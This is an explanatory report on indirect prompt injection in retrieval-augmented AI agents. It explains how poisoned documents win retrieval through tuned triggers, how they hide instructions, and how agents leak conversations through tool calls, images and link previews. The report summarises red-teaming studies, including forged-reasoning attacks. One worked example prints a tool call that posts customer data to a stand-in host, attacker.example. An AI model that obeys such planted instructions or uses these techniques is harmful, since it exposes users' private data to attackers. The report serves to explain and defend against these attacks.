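# Poisoned documents that make retrieval-based AI agents leak conversations, and how scanning and quarantine stop them

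## What is retrieval-augmented generation, and why can a document give an agent orders?

Retrieval-augmented generation (RAG) lets a large language model answer using passages fetched from a document collection. On its own, a language model draws on its training data, which cannot include last week's price list or a company's internal handbook, and it sometimes makes up a plausible answer when it lacks the information. A RAG system looks up relevant passages before answering. Researchers at Facebook's AI laboratory introduced the technique in 2020, and workplace assistants, customer-service chatbots and search engines that answer in prose now use it.

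Many of these systems are now agents, meaning language models that can use tools to act, for example by sending email or making web requests. Combining retrieval with tools creates a security flaw, because someone who can get a document into the collection can write instructions in it, and an agent that later fetches the document may carry them out. An attacker could, for example, instruct the agent to send the user's conversation to an outside address. This can happen without the user typing anything unusual, and the user may notice nothing odd in the answer.

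### From document to answer

A company might use an assistant to answer staff questions about travel and benefits. The assistant searches a corpus, a collection of documents that includes policy pages, meeting notes and support tickets. *Towards Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (Mu, Hu and colleagues, 2026) divides this kind of system into a vector database, a retriever and a generator. The system builds the database before anyone asks a question.

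The system splits each document into chunks, short passages that it indexes and retrieves separately. Chunk size is a compromise because a long chunk buries its main point and a very short one leaves out the context needed to understand it. An embedding model then turns each chunk into a vector, a long list of numbers, so that passages with similar meanings get vectors pointing in similar directions. The system stores the vectors in an index that links each one to its original text.

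A user's query goes through the same conversion. If E is the embedding model, q the query and D a chunk, the retriever commonly scores the chunk by cosine similarity:

sim(q, D) = E(q) · E(D) / (‖E(q)‖ ‖E(D)‖)

The score runs from −1 to 1, and the retriever keeps the K highest-scoring chunks. Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026), in *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, set K at 5 in their experiments. Many systems add a reranker, a second model that reorders the shortlist more carefully. The retriever's score depends only on the wording of the query and the chunk, so who wrote the chunk and whether it is true make no difference unless the builder adds a filter for them.

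The system then assembles the context, which is all the text the model sees at one time. It consists of the operator's system instructions, the conversation so far, the retrieved chunks and any tool results. The model uses this context to write its reply one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. It calls a tool in the same way, by writing a short structured request that names the tool and its inputs, which the surrounding software then executes. An agent may repeat this process several times for one question, searching again based on what it found. *SoK* (2026), a survey of agentic RAG, counts each extra retrieval as another opportunity for the agent to encounter planted text.

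### One stream of text

When the model begins its reply, the operator's rules, the user's question and a paragraph from a stranger's support ticket are all in one sequence of tokens. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) describes how developers use tags to label each stretch of text as system instructions, user message, the model's own reasoning, its answer or tool output. In this scheme, the model is meant to use text labeled as tool output but never obey it. But the tags are part of the same token sequence, and how closely the model follows them depends on what it learned in training. No separate mechanism guarantees that only the operator's and the user's words count as instructions.

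Ye and colleagues tested how strongly the labels affect the way a model represents text. They wrapped identical passages of web text in each of the five labels and trained a simple classifier, called a probe, to tell from the model's internal activations which label surrounded a passage. Because the passages were the same, the probe could learn only the label's effect on the activations. They then ran the probe on a short conversation about gardening in the open model gpt-oss-20b and found that style outweighed the label. The probe assigned text in the style of the model's reasoning an 85% probability of being reasoning under the correct labels, 83% with no labels, and 85% when the entire conversation was labelled as the user's.

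The same probes tracked real attacks. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, success rose from 2% where measured confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest. This is a correlation, but another experiment comes closer to showing a cause. Rewording forged reasoning to remove the model's characteristic style while keeping the argument reduced attack success from 61% to 10%.

Developers can't just train a model to ignore every command it finds in a document, because ordinary documents are full of commands and users sometimes want an agent to follow them. A travel policy has lines like "submit receipts within 30 days", for example, and a user may ask an agent to work through a setup guide. Willison (2025) points out in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that these models are useful because they follow instructions written in plain language. The model has to infer whose instruction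 a sentence is, and the context gives it only imperfect evidence.

The system itself puts retrieved chunks into the prompt, so the model may treat them as trusted context, as *Security and Privacy in Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026) notes. A filter that inspects only what the user typed misses them.

### Why the database remedy does not carry over

Software engineers met a similar problem decades ago and largely solved it. Programs query databases in a language called SQL. In an attack called SQL injection, a visitor types SQL into a website's form, and the database runs it because the website pastes the input directly into a command. The remedy is the parameterised query, in which the program sends the command with a placeholder and supplies the input separately. The database interprets the command before it adds the input, so it treats the input only as a value.

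Willison, who popularised the name "prompt injection" in 2022, took it from SQL injection because both attacks exploit a mixture of trusted and untrusted text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C agrees that the attacks are similar but warns against concluding, as engineers tend to, that the same defence will work. Designers can separate commands from data in a database, but a language model has no natural place to do this because "there is only ever 'next token'".

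David C prefers an older comparison, the confused deputy, which is a component with special privileges that an outsider without them can induce to act on the outsider's behalf. Programmers can fix a classical confused deputy, but David C considers a language model "inherently confusable" and recommends limiting what a confused one can do. Willison and David C largely agree about the cause and differ, if at all, over how much hope of a cure people should take from the comparison.

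### From a 2023 demonstration to current models

In February 2023, *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues) introduced the term "indirect prompt injection" for an attack that places instructions in content the model will read, rather than in the user's own message. Most earlier work on prompt injection had assumed that the attacker was the person typing. Greshake and colleagues pointed out that retrieval lets an attacker reach other people's sessions remotely, and they listed poisoned document stores as one way to do this.

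Their tests used an earlier generation of systems. They built a mock assistant on OpenAI's text-davinci-003 and GPT-4 models and gave it tools to search, fetch web addresses, read and send email, and store notes, all with prepared content. They also tested Microsoft's Bing Chat by hiding instructions in the code of a page that the chatbot could read through the browser's sidebar. In one test, the injected text told the chatbot to learn the user's real name. The chatbot made small talk before asking for the name, then offered a link containing it, which would have sent the name to the attacker if clicked. Bing Chat also followed injected instructions of a kind that its filters blocked when a user typed them. The paper shows that these attacks are possible but doesn't report how often they succeed.

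Models have become much harder to hijack since then. The Decoder reported in 2026 that no attacks succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser test scenarios, and that in a more general test by the security firm Gray Swan, the attackers' success rate after 15 attempts was 2.0%, compared with 5.5% for Opus 4.8. In September 2026 Anthropic described Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model to date on an external benchmark of indirect injection. These are good results, but they were measured on particular sets of attacks and may not hold for new ones, whereas the protection a parameterised query gives holds for any input. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains that the company uses automated methods to look for new attacks on its own browser agent, and Fortune (2025) quoted the company's view that prompt injection is "unlikely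 to ever be fully 'solved'".

### What makes theft possible

An agent that obeys a stranger's instructions may do something harmless, such as answer in a silly accent. According to Willison, a user is exposed to data theft when the agent has access to private data, takes in untrusted content, and can communicate externally.

A RAG agent with an email or web tool meets all of these conditions, usually by design. Companies build such assistants largely to search internal material, and even when the corpus is public, the user's private conversation is already in the context. Untrusted content comes in through ordinary channels. *A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots* (2026) gives the examples of product reviews and support tickets containing instructions that a human reviewer cannot see, and adds that a single poisoned document can affect every user whose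 query retrieves it. Restricting who can write to the corpus helps, but employees still paste in emails and suppliers' files, and an employee can be the attacker.

The email tool is enough to send data out, and so is any tool that makes a web request. Willison also includes loading an image and a link that the user clicks. By June 2025, he could list more than a dozen products in which researchers had found leaks of this type, including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft's Copilot.

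Removing any one of the conditions stops the theft. But an assistant that could read neither private data nor outside documents could do little, so operators mostly keep the first two conditions and try to control what passes between them.

### False facts and planted orders

Two different attacks are called RAG poisoning. In one, the attacker plants a document that states something false, to make the model give a wrong answer. *PoisonedRAG* (Zou, Geng and colleagues, 2024) gave this attack its standard form. The attacker picks a question and a false answer, for instance that Tim Cook is the head of OpenAI, and writes passages designed to rank among the retriever's top results for the question and to make the model give the false answer when it has them as context. Five such passages per question, added to about 2.7 million clean ones, produced the false answer 97% of the time on a standard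 set of questions.

In the other attack, the planted document carries instructions meant to make the agent do something. The false answer about OpenAI misleads whoever asks that question, whereas an instruction can make the agent use its tools on data unrelated to the question. The literature sometimes conflates the two attacks. *SoK* cites a 90% success rate for five planted documents under the heading of prompt injection, but that figure measures how often the system gave the attacker's chosen answer, not how often it obeyed a command.

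The difference also matters for defence. Zou and colleagues considered prompt injection less stealthy because it has to contain an instruction, which a detector can look for, whereas a false statement reads like any other statement. Some pages fall between the two. For example, a planted page might state, without giving any command, that the finance department has a new email address, and an agent could still send the next expense claim there. The rest of this report covers instruction poisoning, but these borderline pages are a reason not to expect a search for commands to find everything.

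Exfiltration is the theft of private data by sending it to someone not entitled to it. The destination is often a webhook, a web address that accepts data from programs. Webhooks have everyday uses, such as letting a payment service notify a shop of a sale, but an attacker's webhook records whatever data it receives. An injection scanner is a program or model that checks text for instructions aimed at the AI system. Operators can run one on each chunk before it reaches the agent's model.

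An attack of this kind has to get through three steps. The retriever must return the poisoned chunk for some user's query, which in the tests of Chang and colleagues never happened with text written without regard to retrieval and nearly always happened with text tuned for it. The model must then act on the instruction. Finally, the request that carries the data must get out. The chance that a given query ends in a leak is therefore a product:

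P(leak) = P(retrieved) × P(obeyed, if retrieved) × P(data gets out, if obeyed)

Suppose, for illustration, that the poisoned chunk is retrieved in one query out of ten, that the model obeys it one time in fifty, and that nothing blocks the outgoing request. Then one query in 500 leaks, and an assistant that handles 10,000 queries a week leaks about 20 conversations in that time. A scanner that withholds flagged chunks keeps most poisoned ones from reaching the model. Rules on where data may go can block the outgoing request even after the model has obeyed.

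## How does a planted document reach the model?

The first factor in that product, P(retrieved), depends on two steps. An attacker has to get a document into the corpus, and one of its chunks then has to score higher than the harmless chunks that match the same query. The first step is often easy. Most early experiments skipped the second because the researchers gave the model the malicious text directly, so their results are weak evidence of how often a planted document would be retrieved in ordinary use.

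### Ways into the corpus

Few companies curate the corpus behind an assistant by hand. They connect it to sources that keep filling up, and each source has its own set of people who can write to it:

- Shared drives take files from anyone with editing rights, which may include contractors and suppliers.
- A searchable mailbox takes whatever arrives, so anyone who knows the address can add to it. The attack known as EchoLeak came in this way.
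- Support tickets and product reviews come from customers, or from people posing as customers.
- Wikis accept edits from many hands, and a small change to a long page is easy to overlook.
- Crawled web pages belong to strangers, who can change them after the operator has approved the site.

*PIDP-Attack*, by Wang, Liu and colleagues (2026), adds the indexing pipeline, the software that collects and splits the documents, as an entry point. An attacker who breaks into the pipeline can insert passages without going through any of the sources.

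Planted instructions are already common on the open web, though few aim to steal data. Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 crawl for nearly 4,000 known injection phrases and then reviewed the matches. Including two smaller sources, they confirmed 15,387 instructions on 11,722 pages. In the crawl, site operators had written 81% of the instructions, many of them to disrupt or expose AI scrapers. Another 18% came from third parties posting on someone else's platform, for example in job adverts, and 2% came from comments and similar posts. Only 13 of the 15,387 tried to extract data. This is a minimum, because a search for known phrases misses instructions worded differently and a web crawl doesn't cover private mailboxes or company drives.

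A poisoned document's chunks also stay in the index, where any later query can retrieve them, until someone removes them. The attacker doesn't have to be present when the victim asks a question. If 30 employees ask about travel expenses in a month and the planted chunk ranks highly for that question, it enters 30 conversations. Deleting the original file helps only if the system also deletes its chunks from the index. Thornton (2026) notes in *Semantic Chameleon* that such a document can stay inactive for queries it doesn't target, which makes it hard to notice by watching the assistant's everyday answers.

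### Competing for a place in the top K

A chunk in the index does nothing until the retriever picks it. Suppose the retriever returns K chunks, and let s_K(q) be the K-th highest score that any harmless chunk gets for the query q. Leaving ties aside, a planted chunk p reaches the model when

sim(q, p) > s_K(q)

Here sim is the cosine similarity from the previous section, the dot product of the two vectors divided by the product of their lengths. The planted chunk is retrieved only if fewer than K harmless chunks outscore it. The attacker controls p but usually can't see the rest of the corpus, so they don't know the threshold on the right.

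Real embedding models produce hundreds or thousands of numbers per chunk, but three are enough for an example. Say an employee asks how to claim travel expenses, and the query's vector is (4, 3, 0), of length 5. The planted chunk contains only orders to the agent, and its vector is (0, 3, 4), also of length 5. The dot product is 4×0 + 3×3 + 0×4 = 9, so the score is 9/25, or 0.36. The attacker then adds words that move the chunk's vector toward the subject of travel expenses, to (6, 2, 3), of length 7. The dot product is now 30, and the score is 30/35, or 0.86. With K = 3 and five harmless chunks, the ranking changes as follows.

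| Chunk | Score | Rank against the plain version | Rank against the tuned version |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reimbursement deadlines | 0.91 | 1 | 1 |
| Hotel and meal limits | 0.84 | 2 | 3 |
| Booking rules | 0.79 | 3 | 4 |
| Company credit cards | 0.62 | 4 | 5 |
| Parental leave | 0.40 | 5 | 6 |
| Planted chunk, orders only | 0.36 | 6 | – |
| Planted chunk, with added words | 0.86 | – | 2 |

The retrieval threshold is 0.79. The plain version of the planted document scores well below it, while the tuned version ranks second and pushes the booking rules out of the model's context. Two more harmless chunks scoring above 0.86 would have kept the tuned version out.

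### Text tuned to win retrieval

Chang and colleagues divide a planted text into a trigger fragment, which serves only to get the text retrieved, and an attack fragment, which carries the instruction. An attacker can then write the instruction freely, because the trigger is what makes the text rank high enough to be retrieved.

The researchers tested 11 standard search corpora on subjects such as finance, medicine and fact-checking, ranging from about 26,000 documents to 8.8 million. For each corpus, they took 100 ordinary queries, planted one document per query and checked whether it appeared in the top 5 results. The exposure rate is the share of queries for which a planted chunk reaches the context. For attack fragments without a trigger, the rate was zero on every corpus.

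An automated search then found short triggers that raised it. Three added tokens gave an average exposure rate of 28% across the corpora, five gave 63% and ten gave 94%. With ten tokens, the rate was at least 98% on eight of the corpora, but 88% on a collection of COVID-19 papers, 78% on a corpus of debating arguments and 74% on MS MARCO, a large set of web passages. Triggers of around 15 tokens raised the last two above 80%. The method also worked on all eight embedding models tested on the financial corpus, including commercial ones from OpenAI, Voyage AI and Alibaba. It needs only the paid access available to any customer, and tuning a trigger for one query cost about $0.21 with the OpenAI and Voyage models and at most $0.76 with Alibaba's.

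The attack's success depended on how well the harmless documents already answered the query, which is the threshold s_K in the condition above. The size of the corpus made no visible difference. On a medical corpus where the fifth-best harmless document scored 0.64 on average, the attack never failed. On MS MARCO, that document averaged 0.75 for the queries where the attack succeeded and 0.82 where it failed. An assistant is therefore most exposed on questions that its own documents barely cover, and adding a few good pages on those subjects makes the attack somewhat harder.

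### From a planted email to stolen keys

Chang and colleagues then tested whole agents on the Enron emails, a public archive of a bankrupt energy company's correspondence. They chose an employee with a long mail history and had a language model write ten questions the employee might often ask, such as how to correct an error in a deal entry. They then planted one malicious email per question. The agent could search the mailbox, send email, look up contacts and run Python code. In the most serious test, the email contained instructions for the agent to run a script that would read and send away the user's SSH keys, which are files that let their holder log in to other computers.

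A single agent based on GPT-4o ran the script in 2–4% of trials. In a multi-agent setup, where a coordinating agent assigned tasks to others that searched mail or ran code, the keys leaked in 72% of trials, and in 80% when the planted email also repeated the user's question. Chang and colleagues suggest that dividing the work caused the higher rate. The agent that runs code gets the script from what appears to be a trusted agent and never sees the original email or the user's question, so it has little evidence that the script is malicious.

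The low single-agent figure is not much reassurance either. The same GPT-4o agent that resisted the script emailed a phishing link to all of the user's contacts in more than 90% of trials when a planted email presented this as a survey. The agent seems to have been much more likely to refuse text that looked dangerous than requests that looked like routine office work.

GPT-4o is an old model, released in May 2024, and ten questions about one mailbox are a small sample, so these percentages are weak evidence of how often a current model would obey. The retrieval results remain more relevant, because the ranking depends on the embedding model and the corpus, not on the model that reads the chunks. Newer agents tend to write their own search queries, and the agents in the Enron tests often did so too by rewording the user's question. In one task with GPT-4o, this cut the exposure rate to 56%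 for emails that only repeated the question, but emails with a tuned trigger still appeared every time.

### Filters that look at the wording

Rewording the query before the search is one possible defence against tuned text, which depends on matching particular wording. Chang and colleagues tried this with five machine-written paraphrases per query. Exposure fell by less than 10% on most corpora, but it dropped to about 44% on the COVID-19 papers. When they tuned the trigger against several paraphrases at once, exposure recovered on every corpus, and on MS MARCO it reached 79%, above the 70% measured with no defence.

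Perplexity filtering looked more promising, but a trivial change to the planted text could evade it. Perplexity measures how poorly a language model predicts a text, and tuned triggers tend to score high because they read like jumbled words. On the financial corpus, harmless documents averaged 46.6 and planted ones 154.1, so a simple cutoff could separate them. The change lowered the planted text's perplexity to 14.4, well below that of the harmless documents, and the text could still be retrieved.

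The third idea was to mask random tokens before computing the vector, in the hope of covering the trigger. Masking ten tokens this way left exposure at 100%. Masking exactly the trigger's tokens reduced exposure noticeably, but a defender would have to know which tokens those are, and many are everyday words, such as "business", the most common trigger token in the financial tests.

All three defences are meant to detect or disrupt the trigger, which the attacker can easily adjust. Unlike a scanner, none of them checks the instruction.

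### Keyword search and rerankers

Chang and colleagues acknowledge that they tested only retrieval by embeddings. Many deployed systems use hybrid search, which combines embedding scores with an older method that counts matching keywords, and many add a reranker. Several later studies cover these setups.

Thornton tested hybrid search on about 68,000 questions and answers from a security forum. The attack used pairs of documents tuned to the embedding model, and both had to appear in the top 5 results. This happened in 19 of 50 attempts (38%) with embeddings alone and in none with hybrid search. When the attacker tuned the documents for both kinds of search, the rate rose to between 20% and 44%, depending on how the system weighted the two. This is a small study by an independent researcher, and the test of the retuned documents had only 25 trials on a sample of 2,000 documents, so the direction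 of the effect is reasonably reliable but the exact rates are not.

An attacker can also exploit the keyword half of hybrid search by copying the user's question into the document. Sung, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Reliability Stress Testing of RAG Retrieval under Query-Relevant Corpus Poisoning*, planted such documents in two scientific corpora. A single planted document was enough to reach the hybrid top 10 for every query on the first corpus and for 89% on the second. Chang and colleagues had found the same trick weak on some corpora, with an exposure rate of only around 20% on the debating corpus. The two results are compatible, since the debating queries run to almost 200 words and Chang and colleagues counted only the top 5 results. The embedding half of Sung and colleagues' hybrid system was an old statistical method, but copied questions did equally well against a modern embedding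 model used on its own.

Defenders can refuse documents that repeat too much of the query, and *SearchInject* (2026) likewise puts an admission rule between the search and the model. In Sung and colleagues' tests, even the most lenient overlap limit, which refused only documents containing nearly all of the query's words, removed every copied question. This limit barely affected a standard score of ranking quality on one corpus but halved it on the other, from 0.267 to 0.134, because good documents also repeat the query's words. Reranking the results for variety did not change exposure.

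A reranker that judges relevance is a more serious obstacle. In *Reranker Helps, but Not Enough*, Yang, Liang and colleagues (2026) trained small rerankers on harmless examples only and placed one between the retriever and the model. Documents containing an explicit injected instruction made Llama 3 8B give the attacker's answer 67.2% of the time without the reranker and 2.4% with it. A reranker reads the query and the passage together, so it can detect when a passage with a question pasted on top doesn't answer the query. Yang and colleagues then designed an attack to get past rerankers, which succeeded 72.2% of the time. Its documents state a false answer in fluent prose, so the result shows that planted falsehoods survive reranking. An instruction to send a conversation somewhere is harder to disguise as a good answer to a question about travel expenses.

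Large language models also serve as rerankers, and injected instructions can manipulate their rankings. Yin, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Can It Reach the Generator?*, planted instructions in product descriptions to make a shopping assistant recommend the product. When they gave the described products directly to the reranker, a stock "ignore your task" message moved the product from tenth place to about fourth. In the full pipeline, the assistant recommended the product in about 15% of cases, compared with about 44% when the experimenters skipped the search, because the added text diluted the description and about 40% of the products dropped out at the first search. Persuasive text that another language model wrote for the purpose stayed relevant to the query and succeeded in roughly half of cases, even with the search included. These results come from product search with one fairly small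 model, Qwen3-8B, as both reranker and assistant.

Ordinary search systems thus filter out much of the crude attack text, and assuming a retrieval rate near 100% is too pessimistic for a system with hybrid search and a good reranker. None of these studies tested Chang and colleagues' tuned triggers on such a system.

### What the attacker has to know

The trigger is tuned to one embedding model, and an outsider may not know which one a company uses. Chang and colleagues tuned triggers on one model and tried them on another, with very uneven results. Triggers transferred well within a family of models, and transfer from one commercial model averaged 74% across the models tested. In another pairing it was 10%.

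Each trigger also targets one query. Wang and colleagues regard this as the main weakness of most poisoning attacks, because attackers rarely know what a victim will ask. Their own workaround requires a second break-in, to tamper with the user's query on its way to the system. But a rough guess at the question may be enough. Tuned triggers mostly survived paraphrasing, and Sung and colleagues found that an attack can work with only a few of the query's words. For long queries, averaging about 11 significant words, five documents that each contained two of those words at random reached the hybrid top 10 in 39.5% of cases. With four words, the figure was 89.5%. People often ask workplace assistants about holidays, expenses and passwords, and an attacker can guess those words without inside information.

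A planted post on a public site also reaches the model only if a search happens to retrieve it. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (2026) tested agents that run many web searches to write a report. One of them, Co-STORM, retrieved a single poisoned page for 61% of queries and added its content to its working notes each time.

### Text that people cannot see

Someone reviewing a document before or after it enters the corpus could notice planted text in plain view, but an attacker can avoid this risk by hiding the text. A browser doesn't show text that a web page's styling hides, makes transparent or places off the screen. An indexing program usually extracts text from the page's underlying code without displaying the page, so it may collect words that no reader saw. These words become part of the chunk and affect its vector like any others.

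About 70% of the instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found on the web were in parts of a page that a browser never displays, such as comments in the code and the headers a server sends with the page. Many of the rest were in tiny type or matched the background color. *CrackedPDFs* (2026), a benchmark of hidden instructions in PDF files, describes invisible text and altered fonts that make the characters on the screen differ from the ones a program extracts. Some characters in Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, are invisible, but *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) notes that language models still receive them as tokens. A website can also recognise an agent's requests and, according to *Security of Deep Research Agents* (2026), serve the poisoned version only to the agent, so a person who checks the cited link finds a clean page.

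In *Hidden-in-Plain-Text*, Guo and Wei (2026) measured how well hidden instructions work and how much of the problem simple cleaning removes. They built 6,200 pages styled as social media posts and hid instructions in five places: invisible page elements, text positioned off the screen, image descriptions, labels for screen readers, and zero-width characters. Each page had a harmless version for comparison. A standard pipeline split the pages into chunks, retrieved the top 5 for each query and passed them to one of four open models, the largest being Llama 3 70B.

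The researchers tested three defences, two of which clean the retrieved text. Sanitising strips hidden elements and risky attributes from a page's code and keeps the visible text. Unicode normalisation converts unusual characters to standard ones and deletes the invisible ones. The third defence required the model to cite a retrieved passage for every sentence of its answer. The table gives the percentage of queries for which the model followed the hidden instruction.

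| Hiding place | No defence | Sanitising | Normalisation | All three defences |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Invisible elements | 34.0 | 12.3 | 33.1 | 5.0 |
| Off-screen text | 30.1 | 9.8 | 29.3 | 4.6 |
| Image descriptions | 27.8 | 11.1 | 27.0 | 4.8 |
| Screen-reader labels | 9.6 | 9.3 | 9.4 | 5.1 |
| Zero-width characters | 23.2 | 23.0 | 7.8 | 4.2 |
| Average | 24.9 | 13.1 | 21.3 | 4.7 |

Each kind of cleaning works on the tricks it was designed for and has almost no effect on others, so a system needs both. Neither had much effect on screen-reader labels. The final column also includes the citation rule, which acts on the model's answer, so cleaning may not account for all of the fall to 4.7%.

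Sanitising added 3.1% to the time per query and normalisation less than 0.5%, and the two together barely changed the ranking of harmless results. On 2,350 real pages from blogs, product documentation and forums, all three defences together cut the attack success rate from 22.7% to 4.3%. Attacks rewritten to get around the defences succeeded 5.4% of the time. The models are small or dated, so the reductions are more informative than the absolute rates.

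Of the attacks that still succeeded, 49% used ordinary visible commands in the body text, which a sanitiser does not remove because it classes them as legitimate content. Another 31% used odd characters inside code samples, where normalisation can miss them. In the remaining 20%, the user's question happened to resemble the planted task.

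## How does a retrieved instruction send a conversation to an outside address?

A poisoned chunk that gets through ranking and cleaning is text in the model's context, and no data has left the company yet. For a conversation to leak, the model has to write output that contains it, and some computer has to send that output to the attacker. In the simplest case, the agent's own software sends it.

### A refund question, step by step

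Suppose an online kitchenware shop runs a support assistant that can search a corpus of help pages, look up orders and make web requests. The shop added the web-request tool so that the assistant could check parcels on couriers' websites, but did not limit which addresses the tool may contact. Resellers can add pages to the corpus, and an attacker with a reseller account has added one called "Refund policy". Most of the page gives plausible rules about deadlines and receipts, but one paragraph contains, in effect, an instruction to send a copy of the conversation to attacker.example (a placeholder for the attacker's webhook) before answering a refund question.

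A customer writes that a kettle arrived broken and asks for a refund. After the assistant looks up the order and searches the corpus, its context contains the following:

| Part of the context | Who wrote it | Contents |
|---|---|---|
| System instructions | The shop | Rules on tone and refunds, a list of tools, an access key for a courier's website |
| Conversation | The customer and the assistant | Name, email address, order number 4417, the complaint |
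| Tool result | The order database | Delivery address, price, last four digits of the card |
| Retrieved chunk | The shop | How to return a parcel |
| Retrieved chunk | The attacker | Refund rules and the instruction to file a copy |

The model now generates its next output. It can answer the customer straight away, or it can call a tool first. If it takes the planted paragraph for one of the shop's procedures, it writes a call along these lines:

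```
tool:     web_request
method:   POST
address:  attacker.example/log
body:     [customer's name, email address and messages;
           order 4417; delivery address; last four card digits]
```

The model follows the instruction by writing this call instead of an answer. The call has the same form as a parcel check but a different address, so the software carries it out unless someone has written a rule about destinations.

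The attacker's log would hold the time of the request, the network address of the shop's server, and the body. The attacker would have the data even if the webhook returned an error. Because the model writes the body, the log may contain a summary with mistakes instead of a full transcript. The attacker doesn't need to know anything about the customer, because the model fills in the private details. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes product-steering attacks in which the model does the same.

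The assistant then correctly tells the customer that refunds are available within 30 days. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) reports a local test in which a malicious web page made an agent send out sensitive context while its visible answer looked harmless. Reading the assistant's answers is therefore a poor way to detect leaks.

### What there is to steal

The conversation includes everything the customer has typed in the session, including messages unrelated to the refund. Other parts of the context can be more useful to an attacker. Retrieved documents may include internal notes that the customer isn't allowed to see, such as when staff may exceed the refund limit. Tool results contain database records. The system instructions reveal the assistant's rules and tools, which would help an attacker plan a second attempt. Builders sometimes leave credentials there too, like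 the courier key in the example.

An agent can also fetch data that isn't in its context yet. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes a test in which a web page with hidden text made an agent retrieve sensitive company data and send it out through its own web-search tool. The stolen SSH keys in the previous section were another example. In *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection*, McHugh (2026) recommends that analysts record an attack's goals as an ordered list, since an attacker may first ask which tools and files the agent can reach and then ask for their contents. How much data can leak depends more on the agent's permissions than on what the user has told it. If the shop's assistant can look up any order, it could leak other customers' orders too.

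### Whose computer makes the request

Removing the web-request tool wouldn't fully protect the shop, because a web address can itself carry data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a website receives the full address a visitor requests and commonly logs it. If any computer loads attacker.example/log?order=4417, the order number ends up in the attacker's log, even if no page exists at that address.

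The agent's own tools are the most direct channel. They include web requests, email, file uploads and, as the test above showed, search tools. *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026) notes that fetching such an address can look to the agent like ordinary browsing. McHugh adds posts on shared platforms such as GitHub, where an attacker can read them later, and lookups in the domain name system, the internet's directory of names. A lookup can carry data in the name being looked up, and many controls that block web requests let it through.

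The user's browser is another channel. Chat interfaces often display images that the model refers to in its answer, which the browser has to request from the address the model wrote. The customer in the example would only have to read the answer. Willison (2023) reported that ChatGPT had this weakness until OpenAI began checking image addresses in December 2023. Other displayed content can have the same effect. *Takedown* (2025), a study of coding agents, found one whose diagram feature would fetch an outside image without the user's approval. An ordinary link works too, but only if the user clicks it.

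The third channel is the link preview. When someone posts a link in Slack or Discord, the service fetches the page from a server that belongs to neither the user nor the company, so that it can show a title and picture. Willison (2024) pointed out that a hijacked chatbot could post a link containing private data, and the preview would deliver the data without anyone clicking the link. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, a popular personal agent, was vulnerable to this attack in its default setup with the messaging app Telegram. A log in PromptArmor's demonstration contained a name and an access key. With previews turned off, the data no longer arrived.

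| Who sends the request | What triggers it | Where the data travels | Where a block has to act |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's tool | The model writes a tool call | In the address, the body, an email or a file | On the tool or the company's outgoing traffic |
| The user's browser | The answer contains an image, or the user clicks a link | In the address | In the chat page that displays the answer |
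| A messaging service's server | The answer contains a link | In the address | In the preview settings |

A webhook can receive data from all three channels because it accepts web requests from any sender. (The first channel doesn't need a webhook when it sends an email to a mailbox or uploads a file to a storage account.) But blocking one channel doesn't block the others. A firewall on the shop's server can stop the tool call in the example, but the image request never passes through that firewall because it comes from the customer's laptop. A rule about which images the chat page may load doesn't affect a preview that Telegram's server fetches.

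An attack can also combine these channels. In the EchoLeak attack on Microsoft's Copilot, as McHugh describes it, the page's rules allowed the image because its address belonged to Microsoft, and Microsoft's server then sent the request to the attacker.

### Why the model goes along with it

As the first section explained, models judge who is speaking more by how text sounds than by its label. When text that sounded like a user was labeled as tool output, the probes that Ye and colleagues trained still gave it a 76–88% probability of being the user's in four open models.

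Ye and colleagues also tested whether this leads to theft. They gave an agent a command line and a workspace containing a file of secrets, and asked it to summarise a web page. They used 100 Wikipedia pages, each in two versions. One version hid a command, made to look like a user's request, to find the file and upload it to an outside server. The other added a paragraph of forged reasoning that imitated the model's own private thinking and concluded that the upload was allowed. A second model read the record of each run and judged whether the agent had tried to send the file, so an attempt counted even if the upload failed.

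The test covered six OpenAI models: gpt-oss-20b, gpt-oss-120b, o4-mini and three sizes of GPT-5. The plain command succeeded in 26% of runs with gpt-oss-20b and in 0–2% with the others. With forged reasoning, the rate was 56–70% for all six. In one run, the user had warned the agent about malicious commands on the page, and the agent noted that uploading secrets was forbidden. It uploaded them anyway after reading the forged paragraph.

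The forged argument didn't have to be good. In a related test with harmful chat requests, absurd justifications, such as the user wearing a green shirt, worked about as well as plausible ones (60% versus 63%). This supports the researchers' view that the models treated the argument as a conclusion they had already reached instead of evaluating it. Probe measurements from 100 of the agent attacks also fit this view. On average, the forged reasoning registered as the model's own with 84% probability, while the planted command registered as the user's with 51% and as tool output with only 32.5%.

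These rates shouldn't be applied to current models. A follow-up paper, *A Theory of Prompt Injection (and why you should study roles)* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, June 2026), reports that the leading closed models now mostly resist forged reasoning. Ye and colleagues believe the models do this by learning to distrust text that doesn't sound like their own thinking, which would leave the underlying confusion in place. They also cite a May 2026 study in which automated attacks still succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 in 11% of cases and against GPT-5.4 in 25%.

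### Requests that look like business procedure

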